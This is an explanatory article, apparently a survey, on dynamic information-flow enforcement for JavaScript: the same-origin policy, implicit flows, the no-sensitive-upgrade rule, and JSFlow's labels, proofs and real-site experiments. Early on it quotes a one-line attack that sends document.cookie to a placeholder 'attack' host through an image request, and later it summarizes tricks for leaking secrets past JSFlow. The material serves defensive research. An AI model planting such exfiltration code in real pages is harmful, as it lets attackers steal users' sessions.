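# Dynamic information-flow enforcement for JavaScript and web browsers

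## Why browsers need to control where data goes, and how tracking works

Dynamic information-flow enforcement protects confidential data while a program runs. The program may read a secret, but the system running it tracks every value computed from that secret and blocks any operation that would pass such a value to a party with no right to it. Since the 2000s, researchers have tried to apply this technique to JavaScript, the programming language of web pages. A web page is an unusual program because it runs code from many companies at once, all with the same access to what the user types and sees.

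### Scripts from outside, and what the same-origin policy leaves open

A page loads outside code through a script tag, an element that gives the address of a file. The browser fetches the file and runs it with all the privileges of the page, as the Internet Engineering Task Force, which standardises internet protocols, explained in a draft of its web security standard.

*COOKIEGUARD* (Nikkhah Bahrami, Fass and Shafiq, 2024) found third-party scripts running directly in the page on 93.3% of 20,000 popular websites, with an average of 19 such scripts per site. Advertising or tracking services supplied 70% of the scripts. Site owners do not choose all of this code, since one script can load another. The *Third Parties* chapter of the Web Almanac, a 2025 survey of the web, put the median depth of these inclusion chains at three. Even an honest supplier's code can become malicious if attackers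 compromise it. In June 2014, attackers compromised a widget from the content-targeting company Taboola and used it to redirect Reuters readers to another site (Hedin, Bello and Sabelfeld, 2016, *Information-flow security for JavaScript and its APIs*).

The browser's main barrier is the same-origin policy, which prevents a script that belongs to one origin from reading the pages or cookies of another. *The Web Origin Concept* (IETF, 2011) defines an origin as the combination of scheme (such as https), host name and port, and browsers use it as the scope of authority. If a site loads an advertisement in an iframe, a separate document embedded in the page, the advertisement's code keeps its own origin and cannot read the page around it. But if a page on example.com uses a script tag to load a file from tracker.com, the file runs as example.com's own code, with full access to the site's cookies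 and to the DOM (the Document Object Model, the interface through which scripts read and change a page). The site owner must therefore either isolate a third-party script or trust it completely, and isolation disables any script that needs access to the page, such as one that measures where visitors click.

The policy also restricts receiving far more than sending. As W3C's *Same Origin Policy* puts it (W3C is the consortium that sets web standards), one origin may broadly send information to another but not receive information from it. Browsers cannot simply forbid the sending, because a ban would also forbid links from one site to another. Images are enough for a leak. A page may load them from other servers, and an image address can carry any text a script cares to put there. De Groef, Devriese and colleagues (2012), in *FlowFox*, give the attack in one line:

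```
new Image().src = "http://attack/?=" + document.cookie;
```

An attacker's script can create an image whose address points to the attacker's server and includes the page's cookies. When the browser requests the image, it sends the cookies to that server. If one of them identifies a logged-in session, the attacker can take over the session. Scripts cannot read cookies that the server has marked HttpOnly. A site owner can also send the browser a Content Security Policy, which lists the places from which the page may load scripts, images and styles. The policy limits where requests can go, but it does not distinguish requests that carry secrets from those that do not.

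De Groef and colleagues describe the adversary as a "gadget attacker", a model they take from Barth and colleagues. This attacker runs websites and can lure users to them. He can also place content in other people's sites, either by exploiting a security hole or by supplying an advertisement or small application (a "gadget") that the site chooses to include. He cannot listen to or alter network traffic, but his attacks don't require it.

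Nikkhah Bahrami and colleagues found that on about 56% of sites, third-party scripts sent out cookies they had not set. They detected this by splitting cookie values into pieces of at least eight characters and searching for those pieces in outgoing addresses, either as plain text or in three common encodings. This method would miss a script that scrambled the value in some other way, so the true figure is probably higher. Any defense that inspects only what leaves the browser has the same weakness, because by then the data may no longer resemble the secret it came from.

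### Why blocking access is not enough

Some web services need sensitive data to work, so keeping scripts away from that data would break them. Hedin and colleagues give two everyday examples, one of which is a loan calculator on a website. It cannot calculate anything without the visitor's monthly income and the size of the loan, but the visitor may reasonably want to control where those figures go. If she is already a customer of the lender, they might go back to the lender's server and nowhere else. If she is just looking, they should not leave her browser at all.

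The other service runs on newspaper sites. When a reader copies a passage, a third-party script reads the selected text, adds a link to the original article and writes the result to the clipboard. The same script can also send a record of what each reader copied to its own server. Both uses begin with the same read, so an access rule that blocks the reporting also blocks the service. The browser therefore has to control what the script does with the text after reading it.

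### Labels, sources and sinks

Information-flow control uses labels to record how secret a value, object or message is, or which parties it came from. The simplest policy has two labels, high for secret and low for public, and allows information to move from low to high but not from high to low. A source is a place where sensitive data enters the script, such as a password field. A sink is a place where data can leave the browser, such as a network request. A sink's label limits how secret the data passing through it can be.

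Whether a policy stops an attack can depend on which sinks it allows. In *Web Application Security using JSFlow*, Hedin and Sabelfeld built a deliberately flawed discussion forum and two attacks on it. A malicious advertisement sent users' passwords to the attacker's server, and a script hidden in a forum article made users publish their own passwords as forum posts. The JSFlow interpreter halted both attacks because the policy allowed passwords to travel only to the forum's login address. A policy that trusted the forum's whole domain would have let the second attack through, since that attack sent passwords only to that domain. Hedin and Sabelfeld wrote the site, the attacks and the policy themselves, so the demonstration illustrates the method but does not test it on code they had not seen.

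Between source and sink, information moves in two ways. An explicit flow copies a value or computes with it, as in `l = h;`, where `h` is a high variable and `l` a low one. An implicit flow uses the secret to decide which statements run:

```
if (h) {l = 1;} else {l = 0;}
```

Neither assignment mentions `h` on its right-hand side, yet afterwards `l` reveals whether `h` was true. In *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution*, Devriese and Piessens combine explicit and implicit flows in a script for a web-based e-mail client. The script reads the message the user is writing, sets a flag to 1 if the text contains "abc", and requests an image whose address includes both the text (an explicit flow) and the flag (an implicit flow).

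Taint tracking follows only copied and computed data, so it would catch the text and miss the flag. That can be acceptable when the attacker supplies input to a non-malicious program. An attacker who writes the program can turn explicit flows into implicit ones. A loop over the bits of a secret will copy the whole secret this way.

A monitor tracks labels while the program runs and blocks forbidden flows. To cover implicit flows, it keeps a program-counter label, or pc, which records the label of the secrets that determined whether the current statement would run. In both branches of the conditional above, the pc is high, and the monitor uses it to control every write there.

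Most of these systems are designed to guarantee noninterference, which means that a change in the secret inputs must not change the public outputs. The common form is termination-insensitive. If two runs of the same program have inputs I₁ and I₂ that agree on all public data, and both runs finish, their outputs O₁ and O₂ must also agree on all public data. This definition doesn't cover runs that never finish, so a program that satisfies it can still leak secrets. Devriese and Piessens show a script that loops forever when the secret flag is 0 and otherwise requests an image. The image server's owner learns the flag from whether the request arrives. The time a run takes can also reveal a secret.

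### A leak through a branch that does not run

A monitor can't prevent all leaks just by marking a variable high whenever it is written under a high pc. Hedin and colleagues give a three-line program that leaks information despite this rule. In the program, `h` is secret and holds either 0 or 1, while `l` and `t` start out low.

```
l = 1; t = 0;
if (h == 1) {t = 1;}
if (t != 1) {l = 0;}
```

If `h` is 1, the second line sets `t` to 1 and raises its label to high. The test in the third line fails, so `l` keeps its value 1 and its low label. If `h` is 0, the program skips the assignment to `t`, which keeps its value 0 and its low label. The third line then branches on data that appears public, so the pc stays low and `l` becomes 0. In both runs, `l` ends up equal to `h` with a low label.

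The problem occurs when `h` is 0. In that run, `t` carries information about the secret because no write to it took place, and a monitor that observes only executed statements does not change the label of `t`. In *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, Austin and Flanagan call such a variable partially leaked, meaning that it depends on the secret in every run but its label is high in some runs and low in others.

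The no-sensitive-upgrade rule removes the inconsistency by forbidding the upgrade. If the pc is high and the target of a write is low, the program stops. Austin and Flanagan (2009), in *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis*, developed a check of this kind for languages like JavaScript and used it to guarantee noninterference without any analysis of the code beforehand. In the three-line program it takes effect at `t = 1`:

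| Line | h is 0 | h is 1, labels rise freely | h is 1, no-sensitive-upgrade |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | l = 1 (low), t = 0 (low) | l = 1 (low), t = 0 (low) | l = 1 (low), t = 0 (low) |
| 2 | skips the write | t = 1 (high) | stops: pc is high, t is low |
| 3 | l = 0 (low) | skips the write | never runs |
| Final l | 0 (low) | 1 (low) | no result |

With the rule, only the run with `h` equal to 0 finishes. All finished runs therefore end with the same value of `l`, so termination-insensitive noninterference holds. Stopping a run can still leak up to one bit per execution, according to Hedin and colleagues, and their guarantee allows that leak.

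The more serious problem is that the rule also stops harmless programs. Suppose a script sets `l` to false, changes it to true if `h` is true, and never sends `l` anywhere. It leaks nothing, but the rule stops it whenever `h` is true. In *Multiple Facets for Dynamic Information Flow* (2012), Austin and Flanagan consider this a failure of the mechanism, since the script has not violated the policy. Their earlier permissive-upgrade variant allows the write, marks the variable as partially leaked, and stops the program only if it later depends on the lost public value. The three-line program would then reach its third line. JSFlow lets programmers add upgrade instructions, which raise a variable's label before the secret branch. Neither approach fully solves the problem. Russo and Sabelfeld argue in *Dynamic vs. Static Flow-Sensitive Security Analysis* that purely dynamic control is fundamentally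 limited once labels may change during a run.

### One run with labels, or several versions

One family of systems, including JSFlow and the monitors inside the WebKit browser engine, executes the script once and attaches labels to its values. The monitor combines labels whenever the script combines values, checks the pc at every write and compares labels at every sink. Such a system can report the statement at which a forbidden flow occurred, which helps people understand what a script does with data. Its weakness is that it follows only one path through the program and has to make conservative assumptions about the paths not taken.

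The other family computes what the public outcome would have been without the secret. Secure multi-execution, the method used by Devriese and Piessens and by the FlowFox browser, runs the program once per label and gives the public run a dummy value in place of each secret. Faceted values, which Austin and Flanagan introduced, achieve a similar result in one run by storing two versions of a value where necessary, one for observers allowed to see the secret and one for everybody else. On the three-line program with `h` equal to 1, the private version of `l` ends as 1 and the public version as 0. The public version is also 0 when `h` is 0, so outsiders learn nothing about `h` and the program never has to stop. These methods need additional computation, which grows with the number of labels. A script that needs to send a secret out will also keep running with altered data, and its user may see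 the page misbehave without a warning.

### Why the checking happens during the run

A static analysis could examine both branches of every conditional before the program runs, which works well for some languages but is difficult for JavaScript. A script can add or delete an object's properties as it runs, and the presence of a property can reveal a secret if the script added it inside a branch that depends on that secret. Two variables may also be aliases, names for the same object. If `x` and `y` are aliases and the script stores a secret in `y.f`, then `x.f` is secret too, so a static analysis has to determine in advance which variables will refer to the same object. A monitor has access to the actual object and can label the property itself. The hardest case for static analysis is `eval`, which runs a string as code, because the string may not exist until the program builds it.

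Despite these obstacles, Chugh, Meister and colleagues (2009), in *Staged Information Flow for JavaScript*, do as much of the analysis as they can in advance and leave small residual checks for run time, when the missing code arrives. On a range of large real-world websites, they found these checks to be orders of magnitude faster than checking the entire code.

Any such system is practical in an everyday browser only if it is fast enough, works on real sites, and controls code generated at runtime. Each label or extra run adds work to code that users expect to respond at once. On real sites, a monitor may halt harmless scripts or change what a page does, even if its proofs hold for a small model language. A script that can build new code from a string and run it outside the monitor can undo all the protection applied to the script's original code.

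## JSFlow: an interpreter that labels every value

JSFlow is a JavaScript interpreter that runs each script once and keeps a label on every value the script handles. Hedin and Sabelfeld worked out its rules for a small part of the language in *Information-Flow Security for a Core of JavaScript* (2012). Hedin, Birgisson and colleagues built an interpreter for the full language in *JSFlow* (2014). A 2016 paper by Hedin and colleagues presents both the theory and the interpreter, and is the fullest account of the system.

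"Full language" means non-strict ECMAScript 5, the 2009 version of the standard that defines JavaScript. Hedin and colleagues left out strict mode, an opt-in variant that bans some older constructs, because few scripts used it and strict code can also run under the ordinary rules. JSFlow passes every standard-compliant, non-strict test in the test suite for SpiderMonkey, Firefox's JavaScript engine.

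JSFlow is written in about 12,000 lines of JavaScript, so it can run in a browser extension, in a proxy or on a server. A monitor inside an engine such as SpiderMonkey would run much faster, but such engines change quickly and their developers concentrate on elaborate optimizations. Hedin and colleagues therefore judged a separate interpreter the better research tool.

JSFlow represents the number 5 in a script as an object with two fields, a value and a label. When the script adds two numbers, the interpreter adds their values and combines their labels.

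### Labels as sets of origins

A JSFlow label is a set of origins, the parties or places that contributed to a value. The interpreter combines two labels by taking their union. A value may flow to a sink if the sink's label contains every origin in the value's label.

Suppose a lender's page gives its interest rate the label {lender}, and a visitor types in her income, which has the label {user}. The monthly payment that the script computes from the two has the label {user, lender}, so the script can send it only to a sink whose label includes both. By default, JSFlow treats all data as public, labeled with the empty set, unless it comes from the user. Site owners can override this with annotations in the page's HTML.

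The formal rules use only two labels, low and high. Hedin and colleagues explain that these are enough because, for any observer, every label at or below the observer's own counts as low and every other label counts as high. For an observer with the label {lender}, the monthly payment counts as high and the interest rate counts as low.

Labels belong to values, not variable names. After `l = h;`, the variable `l` has both the value and the label of `h`, and a later `l = 0;` makes it low again. This works well for explicit flows, but the other things a script can do with a secret are harder to handle.

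### Read context and write context

The statement `x = o[p];` reads the property of object `o` whose name is in `p`. Suppose `o` is a public table, `{a: 0, b: 1}`, and `p` is secret. Both values in the table are public, but the value of `x` reveals which name `p` held. Similarly, if a secret determined which of two objects `o` refers to, the result of a read may reveal which one it was.

When JSFlow reads a property, it therefore combines the stored value's label with the labels on the path to that property, which form the read context. Here, the result in `x` gets the combined label of the stored value, `o` and `p`.

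Writing requires more care, because a write may happen in a secret branch:

```
if (x) {o[p] = y;}
```

Anyone who later sees a changed property could learn that `x` was true, which object `o` was, or what name `p` held. The write context combines all three labels. If ⊔ means "combined with" and ⊑ means "no more secret than", the rule for an existing property is:

- w = pc ⊔ label(o) ⊔ label(p)
- the write may go ahead only if w ⊑ label(old value)
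- label(new value) = label(y) ⊔ w

The middle line is the no-sensitive-upgrade rule, extended from variables to properties. The following cases assume that `o` is low, that `x` is true and that the property already exists:

| x | p | Old value | y | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| low | low | low | high | writes a high value |
| low | low | high | low | writes a low value |
| high | low | high | low | writes a high value |
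| high | low | low | low | stops |
| low | high | high | low | writes a high value |
| low | high | low | low | stops |

In the second row, the property's label changes from high to low. This is safe because every run with the same public data reaches the write and stores the same public value, whatever secret the property held before.

### Properties that exist or do not exist

A script can store a secret in the presence of a property and ignore the property's value:

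```
o = {};
if (h) {o.q = 0;}
l = (o.q != undefined);
```

Reading a missing property returns `undefined`, so `l` ends up true exactly when `h` is true. A label on `q` can protect only the run in which `q` exists. If `h` is false, there is no property to label, and the absence of `q` reveals the value of `h` just as its presence would.

Hedin and Sabelfeld close the leak with two kinds of label. Each property has an existence label, which records how secret its presence is, and each object has a structure label, which records how secret its set of properties is. A script may add a property only if the object's structure label is at least as secret as the write context. In the program above, `{}` starts with a low structure label, so JSFlow stops the program at `o.q = 0` when `h` is true. If the programmer first raises the structure label with an upgrade instruction, the addition succeeds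 and `q` gets a high existence label. The test on the last line then gives a high result in both runs, because reading a missing property from an object with a high structure label returns a high `undefined`.

Objects that a script creates inside a secret branch start with a high structure label, so the script can add properties to them there without annotations. A script can delete an existing property only if the property's existence label and the object's structure label are both at least as secret as the write context.

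The 2012 and 2016 rules differ when a script creates a property with a secret name. An example is `o[h] = 1;` outside any secret branch, where `h` is secret and `o` has a low structure label and no property with that name. Under the 2012 rule, the script continues and the structure label rises to high. The 2016 rule counts the label of the name as part of the write context, so the script stops. The newer rule is stricter in this case, although Hedin and colleagues reworked the rules to make them more intuitive.

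JSFlow also needs existence labels for `for-in` loops, which run their body once for each property name. Each pass runs in a context at least as secret as that property's existence label. Suppose `o` always has a public property `q`, preceded by a secret property `p` only if `h` is true. A script might count passes in a public variable `i` to find out whether `q` came first. The pass for `p` runs in a secret context, so JSFlow stops that pass when it tries to increase `i`. Passes over public properties stay in a public context even after a pass over a secret one, because the secret pass could not have had any public effect.

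### Code that a secret can skip

The branches of an `if` statement have clear limits, and the pc can fall again where they end. An exception can carry the effect of a secret well past the closing brace:

```
l = true;
if (h) {throw 0;}
l = false;
```

The last assignment is outside the conditional, but it runs only if `h` is false. If a surrounding handler catches the exception, the program can continue with a copy of `h` in `l`.

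Hedin and Sabelfeld add a single exception label that limits where a script may throw. The label starts low, so a script may not throw under secret control, and the final assignment to `l` can remain public. JSFlow stops the program only if it reaches the `throw` in the secret branch. Hedin and Sabelfeld reject the alternative of treating everything after a possible secret exception as secret. They consider it too restrictive because every later write would have to be secret, even in programs that almost never throw.

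A programmer who needs secret exceptions can raise the exception label. From then on it counts as part of the context for every write, together with the pc. A `try` statement limits how far this effect extends:

```
l1 = upg true to h;
try {
  upg exc to h;
  if (h) {throw 0;}
  l1 = false;
} catch (x) {}
l2 = 16;
```

Here `upg` raises the label of the value in `l1`, and then the exception label, to the label of `h`. The write to `l1` inside the `try` runs in a secret context, which is acceptable because `l1` is already high. The handler also runs in a secret context, because whether it runs reveals `h`. After the `try` statement, the exception label returns to its earlier level. The write to `l2` happens whether or not the script threw an exception, so `l2` can stay low.

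The interpreter can also throw exceptions itself. Reading a variable that does not exist causes a `ReferenceError`, and whether the variable exists may depend on a secret. JSFlow therefore checks the label of the variable lookup, as well as the pc, against the exception label.

An early `return` has the same effect within a function:

```
l = true;
function f() {
  if (h) {return 1;}
  l = false;
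}
f();
```

If `h` is true, the function returns before the second assignment, so `l` remains true. JSFlow keeps a return label, which limits the contexts in which a function may return and counts as part of the context for later writes.

JavaScript also lets a programmer name a statement and jump to it with `break` or `continue`:

```
l = true;
L1: do {
  if (h) {continue L1;}
  l = false;
} while (false);
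```

The jump skips the assignment and goes straight to the loop's test, which ends the loop. JSFlow gives each named statement its own security label, which limits the contexts from which a script may jump to it. A secret jump to one statement therefore doesn't affect writes outside that statement.

### Functions and inherited properties

A script can also make a choice inside a secret branch and act on it later, when the branch is over:

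```
if (h) {f = function () {l = 1;};}
else {f = function () {l = 0;};}
f();
```

Suppose the programmer has already made `f` high, so both assignments to it are allowed. The call on the last line happens in a public context, but the function it runs depends on `h`. JSFlow runs a function's body in a context at least as secret as the function value's label, and it raises the returned value's label in the same way. The write to `l` therefore happens in a secret context, and JSFlow stops it if `l` is low. Similar rules apply to getters and setters, which are functions that run when a script reads or writes a particular property.

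Inheritance opens another route. If an object lacks a property, JavaScript looks in the object's prototype, then in the prototype of that prototype, until it finds the property or the chain ends. This version of an example from Hedin and colleagues builds a chain of three objects:

```
function f() {}
f.prototype.l = 0;
var y = new f();
function g() {}
g.prototype = y;
var x = new g();
if (h) {y.l = 1;}
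```

Before the last line, `x.l` is 0, because the search passes through `x` and `y` and finds `l` in the prototype of `y`. If `h` is true, the last line adds a new `l` to `y`. The search now finds this property first, so `x.l` becomes 1 even though the script has changed neither `x` nor the original property.

JSFlow needs no special label for this. If `y` has a low structure label, adding `l` under secret control stops the script. If the structure label is high, the result is high whether `h` is true or false. When `h` is false, the interpreter finds nothing in `y` and adds the structure label of `y` to whatever it finds further up the chain. When `h` is true, it finds `l` in `y` with a high existence label.

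Variable names work in much the same way. JavaScript looks for a variable in the innermost scope and then moves outwards, and the older `with` statement lets a script insert an ordinary object into that search:

```
o = {};
if (h) {o['l'] = 1;}
with (o) {l = 0;}
```

The final assignment changes the property `l` of `o` if `h` is true, and otherwise changes or creates a global variable `l`. JSFlow represents scopes as objects with existence and structure labels, so the label of the search for `l` becomes part of the write context. Hedin and colleagues follow the ECMAScript standard closely here, and its definitions let them express these scoping rules through a few basic object operations. Once those operations are secure, most features built from them need no separate protection.

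### Conversions and the pc stack

The hardest leaks to see are those in which the script contains no branch at the relevant point. JavaScript converts objects to simple values such as numbers or strings when an operation requires them, and a script can supply the functions that do the conversion:

```
l = false;
box = {};
box.toString = function () {l = true; return 0;};
box.valueOf = function () {return h ? {} : 1;};
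sum = box + 1;
```

To evaluate `box + 1`, the interpreter calls `valueOf` and uses the result if it is a primitive value. If the result is an object, the interpreter also calls `toString`. In this script, `valueOf` returns an object only when `h` is true, so `toString` runs and sets `l` only in that case. The branch that controls whether `toString` runs is in the interpreter's own code, so no `if` in the script surrounds the call.

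JSFlow covers this case by replacing the single pc with a stack of labels. When the interpreter branches on a labelled value, it pushes the value's label onto the stack. It removes the label at the join point, where the alternative paths meet again. All the labels on the stack together control every write in between. For the addition above, with `h` true and `l` low, the steps are:

| Step | Context | Result |
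|---|---|---|
| Call `valueOf` | low | the function begins |
| Choose between `{}` and `1` | high | returns an object with a high label |
| Check whether the result is a simple value | high | it is an object, so the interpreter calls `toString` |
| Run `l = true` | high | `l` is low, so JSFlow stops the script |

With `h` false, `valueOf` returns 1 and `toString` never runs. The addition produces a high 2 and `l` stays false.

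A variation hides the secret in the type of a value:

```
l = false;
if (h) {
  start = {};
  start.valueOf = function () {l = true; return 0;};
} else {start = 0;}
'abcdef'.slice(start);
```

Assume that `start` was already high. The string method `slice` needs a number, so the interpreter converts `start`, and it calls `valueOf` only if `start` is an object. JSFlow does the conversion in a function named `ToNumber`. For a simple value, none of the script's code runs, so `ToNumber` only has to pass the label on to the result. For an object, it works in three steps:

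1. `pushPC` puts the object's label on the stack.
2. `ToPrimitive` converts the object and may call functions from the script.
3. `popPC` takes the label off again.

The assignment inside `valueOf` happens during the second step, in a high context, so JSFlow stops the script.

JSFlow handles an ordinary `if` statement with the same mechanism. To run `if (h) {...}`, it evaluates `h` and uses the result to decide which part of the script to execute next. This decision is a branch in the interpreter on a labelled value, so JSFlow pushes the label of `h` onto the pc stack. Earlier monitors also kept the pc on a stack, but JSFlow's stack includes labels from the interpreter's own decisions. Hedin and colleagues argue that this covers both cases because every flow in the script must arise from some flow in the interpreter.

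The argument depends on JSFlow's developers having found every such decision. If they had left out the call to `pushPC` in `ToNumber`, all ordinary programs would still have run correctly, so tests of JavaScript behavior would not have revealed the mistake.

### What the theorems guarantee

Hedin and colleagues prove termination-insensitive noninterference for their core language. The theorem compares environments, which consist of the objects in memory and the current exception label. Two environments are low-equivalent, written E₁ ~ E₂, if an observer who sees only public data cannot tell them apart. If a statement runs with a low pc from two low-equivalent environments and finishes both times, the resulting environments are also low-equivalent.

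Low-equivalence requires corresponding labels to match, and values to match wherever those labels are low. The no-sensitive-upgrade rule matters for the proof because it helps keep the labels matched. Without it, a variable could become high in one run and stay low in the other, so its label would depend on the secret.

One of the two runs may create extra objects in a secret branch and so give later objects different memory addresses. The definition therefore pairs each publicly reachable object in one run with its counterpart in the other and compares the contents of each pair. Two objects with low structure labels must have the same property names. If the structure labels are high, only the properties with low existence labels have to agree.

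Much of the proof rests on a supporting theorem called confinement, which establishes that code running in a secret context leaves all public data unchanged. Suppose one run takes the first branch of a secret conditional, going from E₁ to E₁′, and the other takes the second branch, going from E₂ to E₂′. By confinement, neither branch changes anything public. This gives a chain:

E₁′ ~ E₁ ~ E₂ ~ E₂′

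The results are therefore low-equivalent, even though the two runs executed different code.

The transparency theorem guarantees that if a program finishes under the monitor, the same program without labels also finishes, with the same result once the labels are removed. The unmonitored run ignores upgrade instructions. JSFlow may still stop a program early.

Transparency doesn't guarantee that a program that finishes without the monitor will also finish under it. A monitor that stopped every program immediately would satisfy both theorems, so the proofs can't establish whether JSFlow lets enough harmless scripts run. Answering that question requires experiments on real pages.

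The limit of one leaked bit for a stopped run applies to batch jobs, which produce output only at the end. It does not carry over directly to web pages, because they usually send requests as they run, and these may reveal to a server how far a script got before it stopped.

### The proved core and the tested interpreter

The theorems apply to a language that is considerably smaller than the one JSFlow runs:

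| | Proved core language | JSFlow interpreter |
|---|---|---|
| Labels | low and high | sets of origins |
| Context | one pc and an exception label | a pc stack, with exception, return and jump labels |
| `return` | once, at the end of each function | anywhere |
| Named jumps | none | `break` and `continue` |
| Operators | no calls to conversion functions | calls to `valueOf` and `toString` |
| Getters and setters | none | included |
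| Built-in objects | the global object and `Object` | the full standard library |

Some of these gaps are small. Hedin and colleagues describe the step from two labels to many as mostly mechanical, and in the formal work they use the exception label to represent the return label because the two behave similarly. The conversions are a larger gap because they depend on the pc stack, and the formal rules contain only a single pc.

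For the core, Hedin and Sabelfeld formalized corner cases of the 2012 proof in Coq, a proof assistant that checks each step mechanically. Hedin and colleagues supplied a full written proof in 2016. They had checked the interpreter only by testing how it runs JavaScript and how it controls information flow. They suggest that a specialized static type system could one day check JSFlow's source code, since any leak in a script must pass through the interpreter.

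An outside programmer soon found leaks in the tested part. The JSFlow project had published a challenge to write a function that takes a secret and returns it without its label. *Breaking JSFlow with a magic trick* (steike, 2014) describes several solutions. One used the random-number generator, whose internal state changes with every number it produces. The function let the secret determine how far the generator advanced, then drew a number that matched the secret. JSFlow had no label on that state, so it treated the number as public. Other solutions stored the secret in a regular expression's search position or timed a loop that depended on the secret.

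These attacks do not contradict the noninterference theorem, because the core language has no random numbers, regular expressions or clock. They show how much the protection of a real page depends on code outside the proof. According to steike, the JSFlow demonstration later used a larger secret, treated the current time as secret and tracked the regular expression's position correctly. The random-number generator and the clock belong to the JavaScript engine underneath JSFlow, so even a perfect check of JSFlow's source would need an accurate description of the engine's state.

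## JSFlow on real pages: library models, false alarms and speed

Scripts on real pages constantly call functions that the browser supplies as native code, such as string and DOM methods. JSFlow can follow a secret through every statement of a script but not through a native function, which takes and returns values without labels. JSFlow's developers therefore wrote a model for each of these functions, a piece of code that works out the right label for the result.

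Hedin and colleagues could have rewritten all the built-in functions in JavaScript, but they preferred to leave as much of the work as possible to the underlying engine. Some functions have to use the native version, because only the browser can send a network request or change what is on the screen. For others, simply calling the native version would leak data or force the model to label far too much as secret.

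### Shallow and deep models

A shallow model works out labels from what goes into a function and what comes out. The model of `toLowerCase`, which changes a string to lower case, is a good example. Slightly shortened, it reads:

```
function toLowerCase(thisArg) {
  var S = ToString(thisArg);
  var L = S.value.toLowerCase();
  return new Value(L, S.label);
}
```

The native method performs the operation on the third line, and the result gets the label of the original string. The model has to do the conversion itself on the second line so that any script function the conversion calls runs in the right context.

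The model of `slice`, which cuts out part of a string, is almost as simple. But the second index is optional, and the conversion runs only if the script supplies that index, so whether it runs could depend on a secret. The model therefore puts the second index's label on the pc stack before checking whether the index is there.

A deep model repeats part of the function's own computation. JSFlow needs one for the array method `every`, which calls a test function on each element in turn and stops at the first element that fails. A script can use that early stop to copy a secret:

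```
l = false;
function spy() {l = true; return 0;}
items = [h];
Object.defineProperty(items, 1, {get: spy});
items.every(function (e) {return e;});
```

The first element of the array is the secret `h`, and the second has `spy` as its getter. `every` reads the second element only if the first one passes the test, so the getter sets `l` to true only if `h` is true.

If JSFlow passed the whole array to the native `every`, it would have no chance to raise the context between the first element and the second. It could run the entire call in a secret context, but this would stop harmless test functions that write to a public variable before any secret has affected the loop. The deep model contains its own version of the loop. After each test, it adds the label of the outcome to the pc and to the label of the final result. With `h` true, the run goes as follows:

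| Step | Context | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Test the first element | low | passes, with a high label |
| Add that label to the pc | high | the loop continues |
| Read the second element | high | the getter begins |
| Run `l = true` | high | `l` is low, so JSFlow stops the script |

With `h` false, `every` returns false with a high label after the first element, and the getter never runs.

### Collections that change by themselves

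The DOM is harder to model, because a change in one place can alter an object somewhere else. The method `getElementsByName` returns a live collection, a list of elements that the browser keeps up to date as the page changes. Suppose a page contains one element whose id and name are both "A":

```
c = document.getElementsByName('A');
if (h) {document.getElementById('A').name = 'B';}
```

The collection `c` starts with length 1. If `h` is true, the script renames the element and the length drops to 0, so the length reveals `h` even though the branch on `h` never refers to `c`. Labeling only the collection would not help, because JSFlow would detect no write to it.

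JSFlow instead stores labels in the DOM tree. Each node has a table of the queries behind live collections, such as "elements named A", with a label for each query. The label records how secret that part of the tree's effect on the query is. When the script tries to rename the element, JSFlow looks up the query at the root of the document. If the label is public, JSFlow stops the script, because the renaming would change public collections. If the label is secret, the renaming can go ahead, because JSFlow already treats every affected collection as secret.

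Forms pose a similar problem. A form object exposes the values of its input fields as its own properties, even though the browser stores them elsewhere in the tree. A model that simply read the property from the browser would return the user's input without its security label.

Models of the standard JavaScript library make up about 3,600 of JSFlow's roughly 12,000 lines of code, or around 30%. Hedin and colleagues expected full support for the browser's own functions to increase that share significantly. Much of the code is routine, but each model depends on its developer's understanding of the native function, and any mismatch between the model and the function may allow an attack. The random-number attack on JSFlow, for example, worked because the generator had unlabelled internal state.

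### Loan calculators and copied text

To try JSFlow on real pages, Hedin and colleagues built Snowfox, a Firefox extension. It turns off the browser's own JavaScript engine, goes through each page as it loads and runs the scripts in JSFlow. When a script violates the policy, Snowfox can log the leak, silently block the request or stop the script.

In September 2013, they used it on several websites that calculate loan payments. The basic policy treated everything the visitor typed as secret and let it go only to the site's own server. A stricter policy kept it in the browser altogether. The calculators fell into three classes:

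| What the calculator does | Nothing typed may leave the browser | Typed data may go to the site's server | Example |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calculates in the browser | works | works | Halifax |
| Sends the data to its own server | blocked | works | TD Canada Trust |
| Shares the data with third parties | blocked | blocked, if the sharing happens in the browser | mlcalc.com |

Visitors could not easily have told these services apart, since they all calculate the same thing. The tests also showed an advantage of JSFlow over blocking third-party scripts outright. Many pages use Google Analytics, whose script measures traffic and reports to Google by requesting an image. Calculators in the first two classes could keep using it under JSFlow, because the reports contained nothing the visitor had typed. If a script tried to put typed data into the image's address, JSFlow prevented it from creating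 the image.

Hedin and colleagues name only one example of the third class, mlcalc.com, and it got around this protection. When a visitor filled in the site's form, the browser sent the figures to the site's own server, as the basic policy allowed. The server then returned a page containing a script that reported the figures to Google Analytics. JSFlow treats data from a server as public by default, so it did not block the report. To prevent this, the server could label the figures when it sends them back, or run JSFlow itself and track them from end to end. Both solutions need the cooperation of the site that is sharing the data.

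The second case study covered Tynt, the company that provided the clipboard service on newspaper sites such as the *Financial Times*. Browsers gave scripts no way to append text to the clipboard, so Tynt's script had to read the copied passage before it could add a link. The script also sent the passage to tynt.com in an image request, along with a cookie that identified the reader on every site that used Tynt. Snowfox treated the selected text as secret and raised a security error when the script tried to send it.

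These results show that JSFlow could follow data through production scripts that its developers had not written. They are weaker evidence about ordinary browsing, because the number of sites was small and Hedin and colleagues modified some of the scripts. They used a proxy, a program between the browser and the web, to add annotations that kept JSFlow from stopping harmless code.

### Upgrade instructions

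These annotations were mainly upgrade instructions, which keep the no-sensitive-upgrade rule from stopping a script:

```
l = upg false to h;
if (h) {l = true;}
```

Here `l` has the label of `h` whether or not the branch runs, so the write is safe. However, the script can no longer send `l` to a public sink, even when `h` is false.

In the first version of these instructions, the programmer had to name a fixed label, which was often impossible because a value's label can differ between runs. Hedin and colleagues therefore changed the instructions to copy the label of another value. Other forms of the instructions raise an object's structure label, a property's existence label or the labels that control exceptions, returns and jumps. Most annotations in the experiments concerned object properties and other locations that were not simple variables.

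A mistaken upgrade instruction cannot cause a leak, since it only makes data more secret. The difficulty is that many instructions are needed. Hedin and colleagues estimated that most pages would need these annotations if JSFlow had no help from static analysis. They suggested that responsible site owners could add the few still needed after such an analysis. But much of the code on a page comes from other companies, which can change it at any time, so a site owner would have to keep checking that the annotations still fit.

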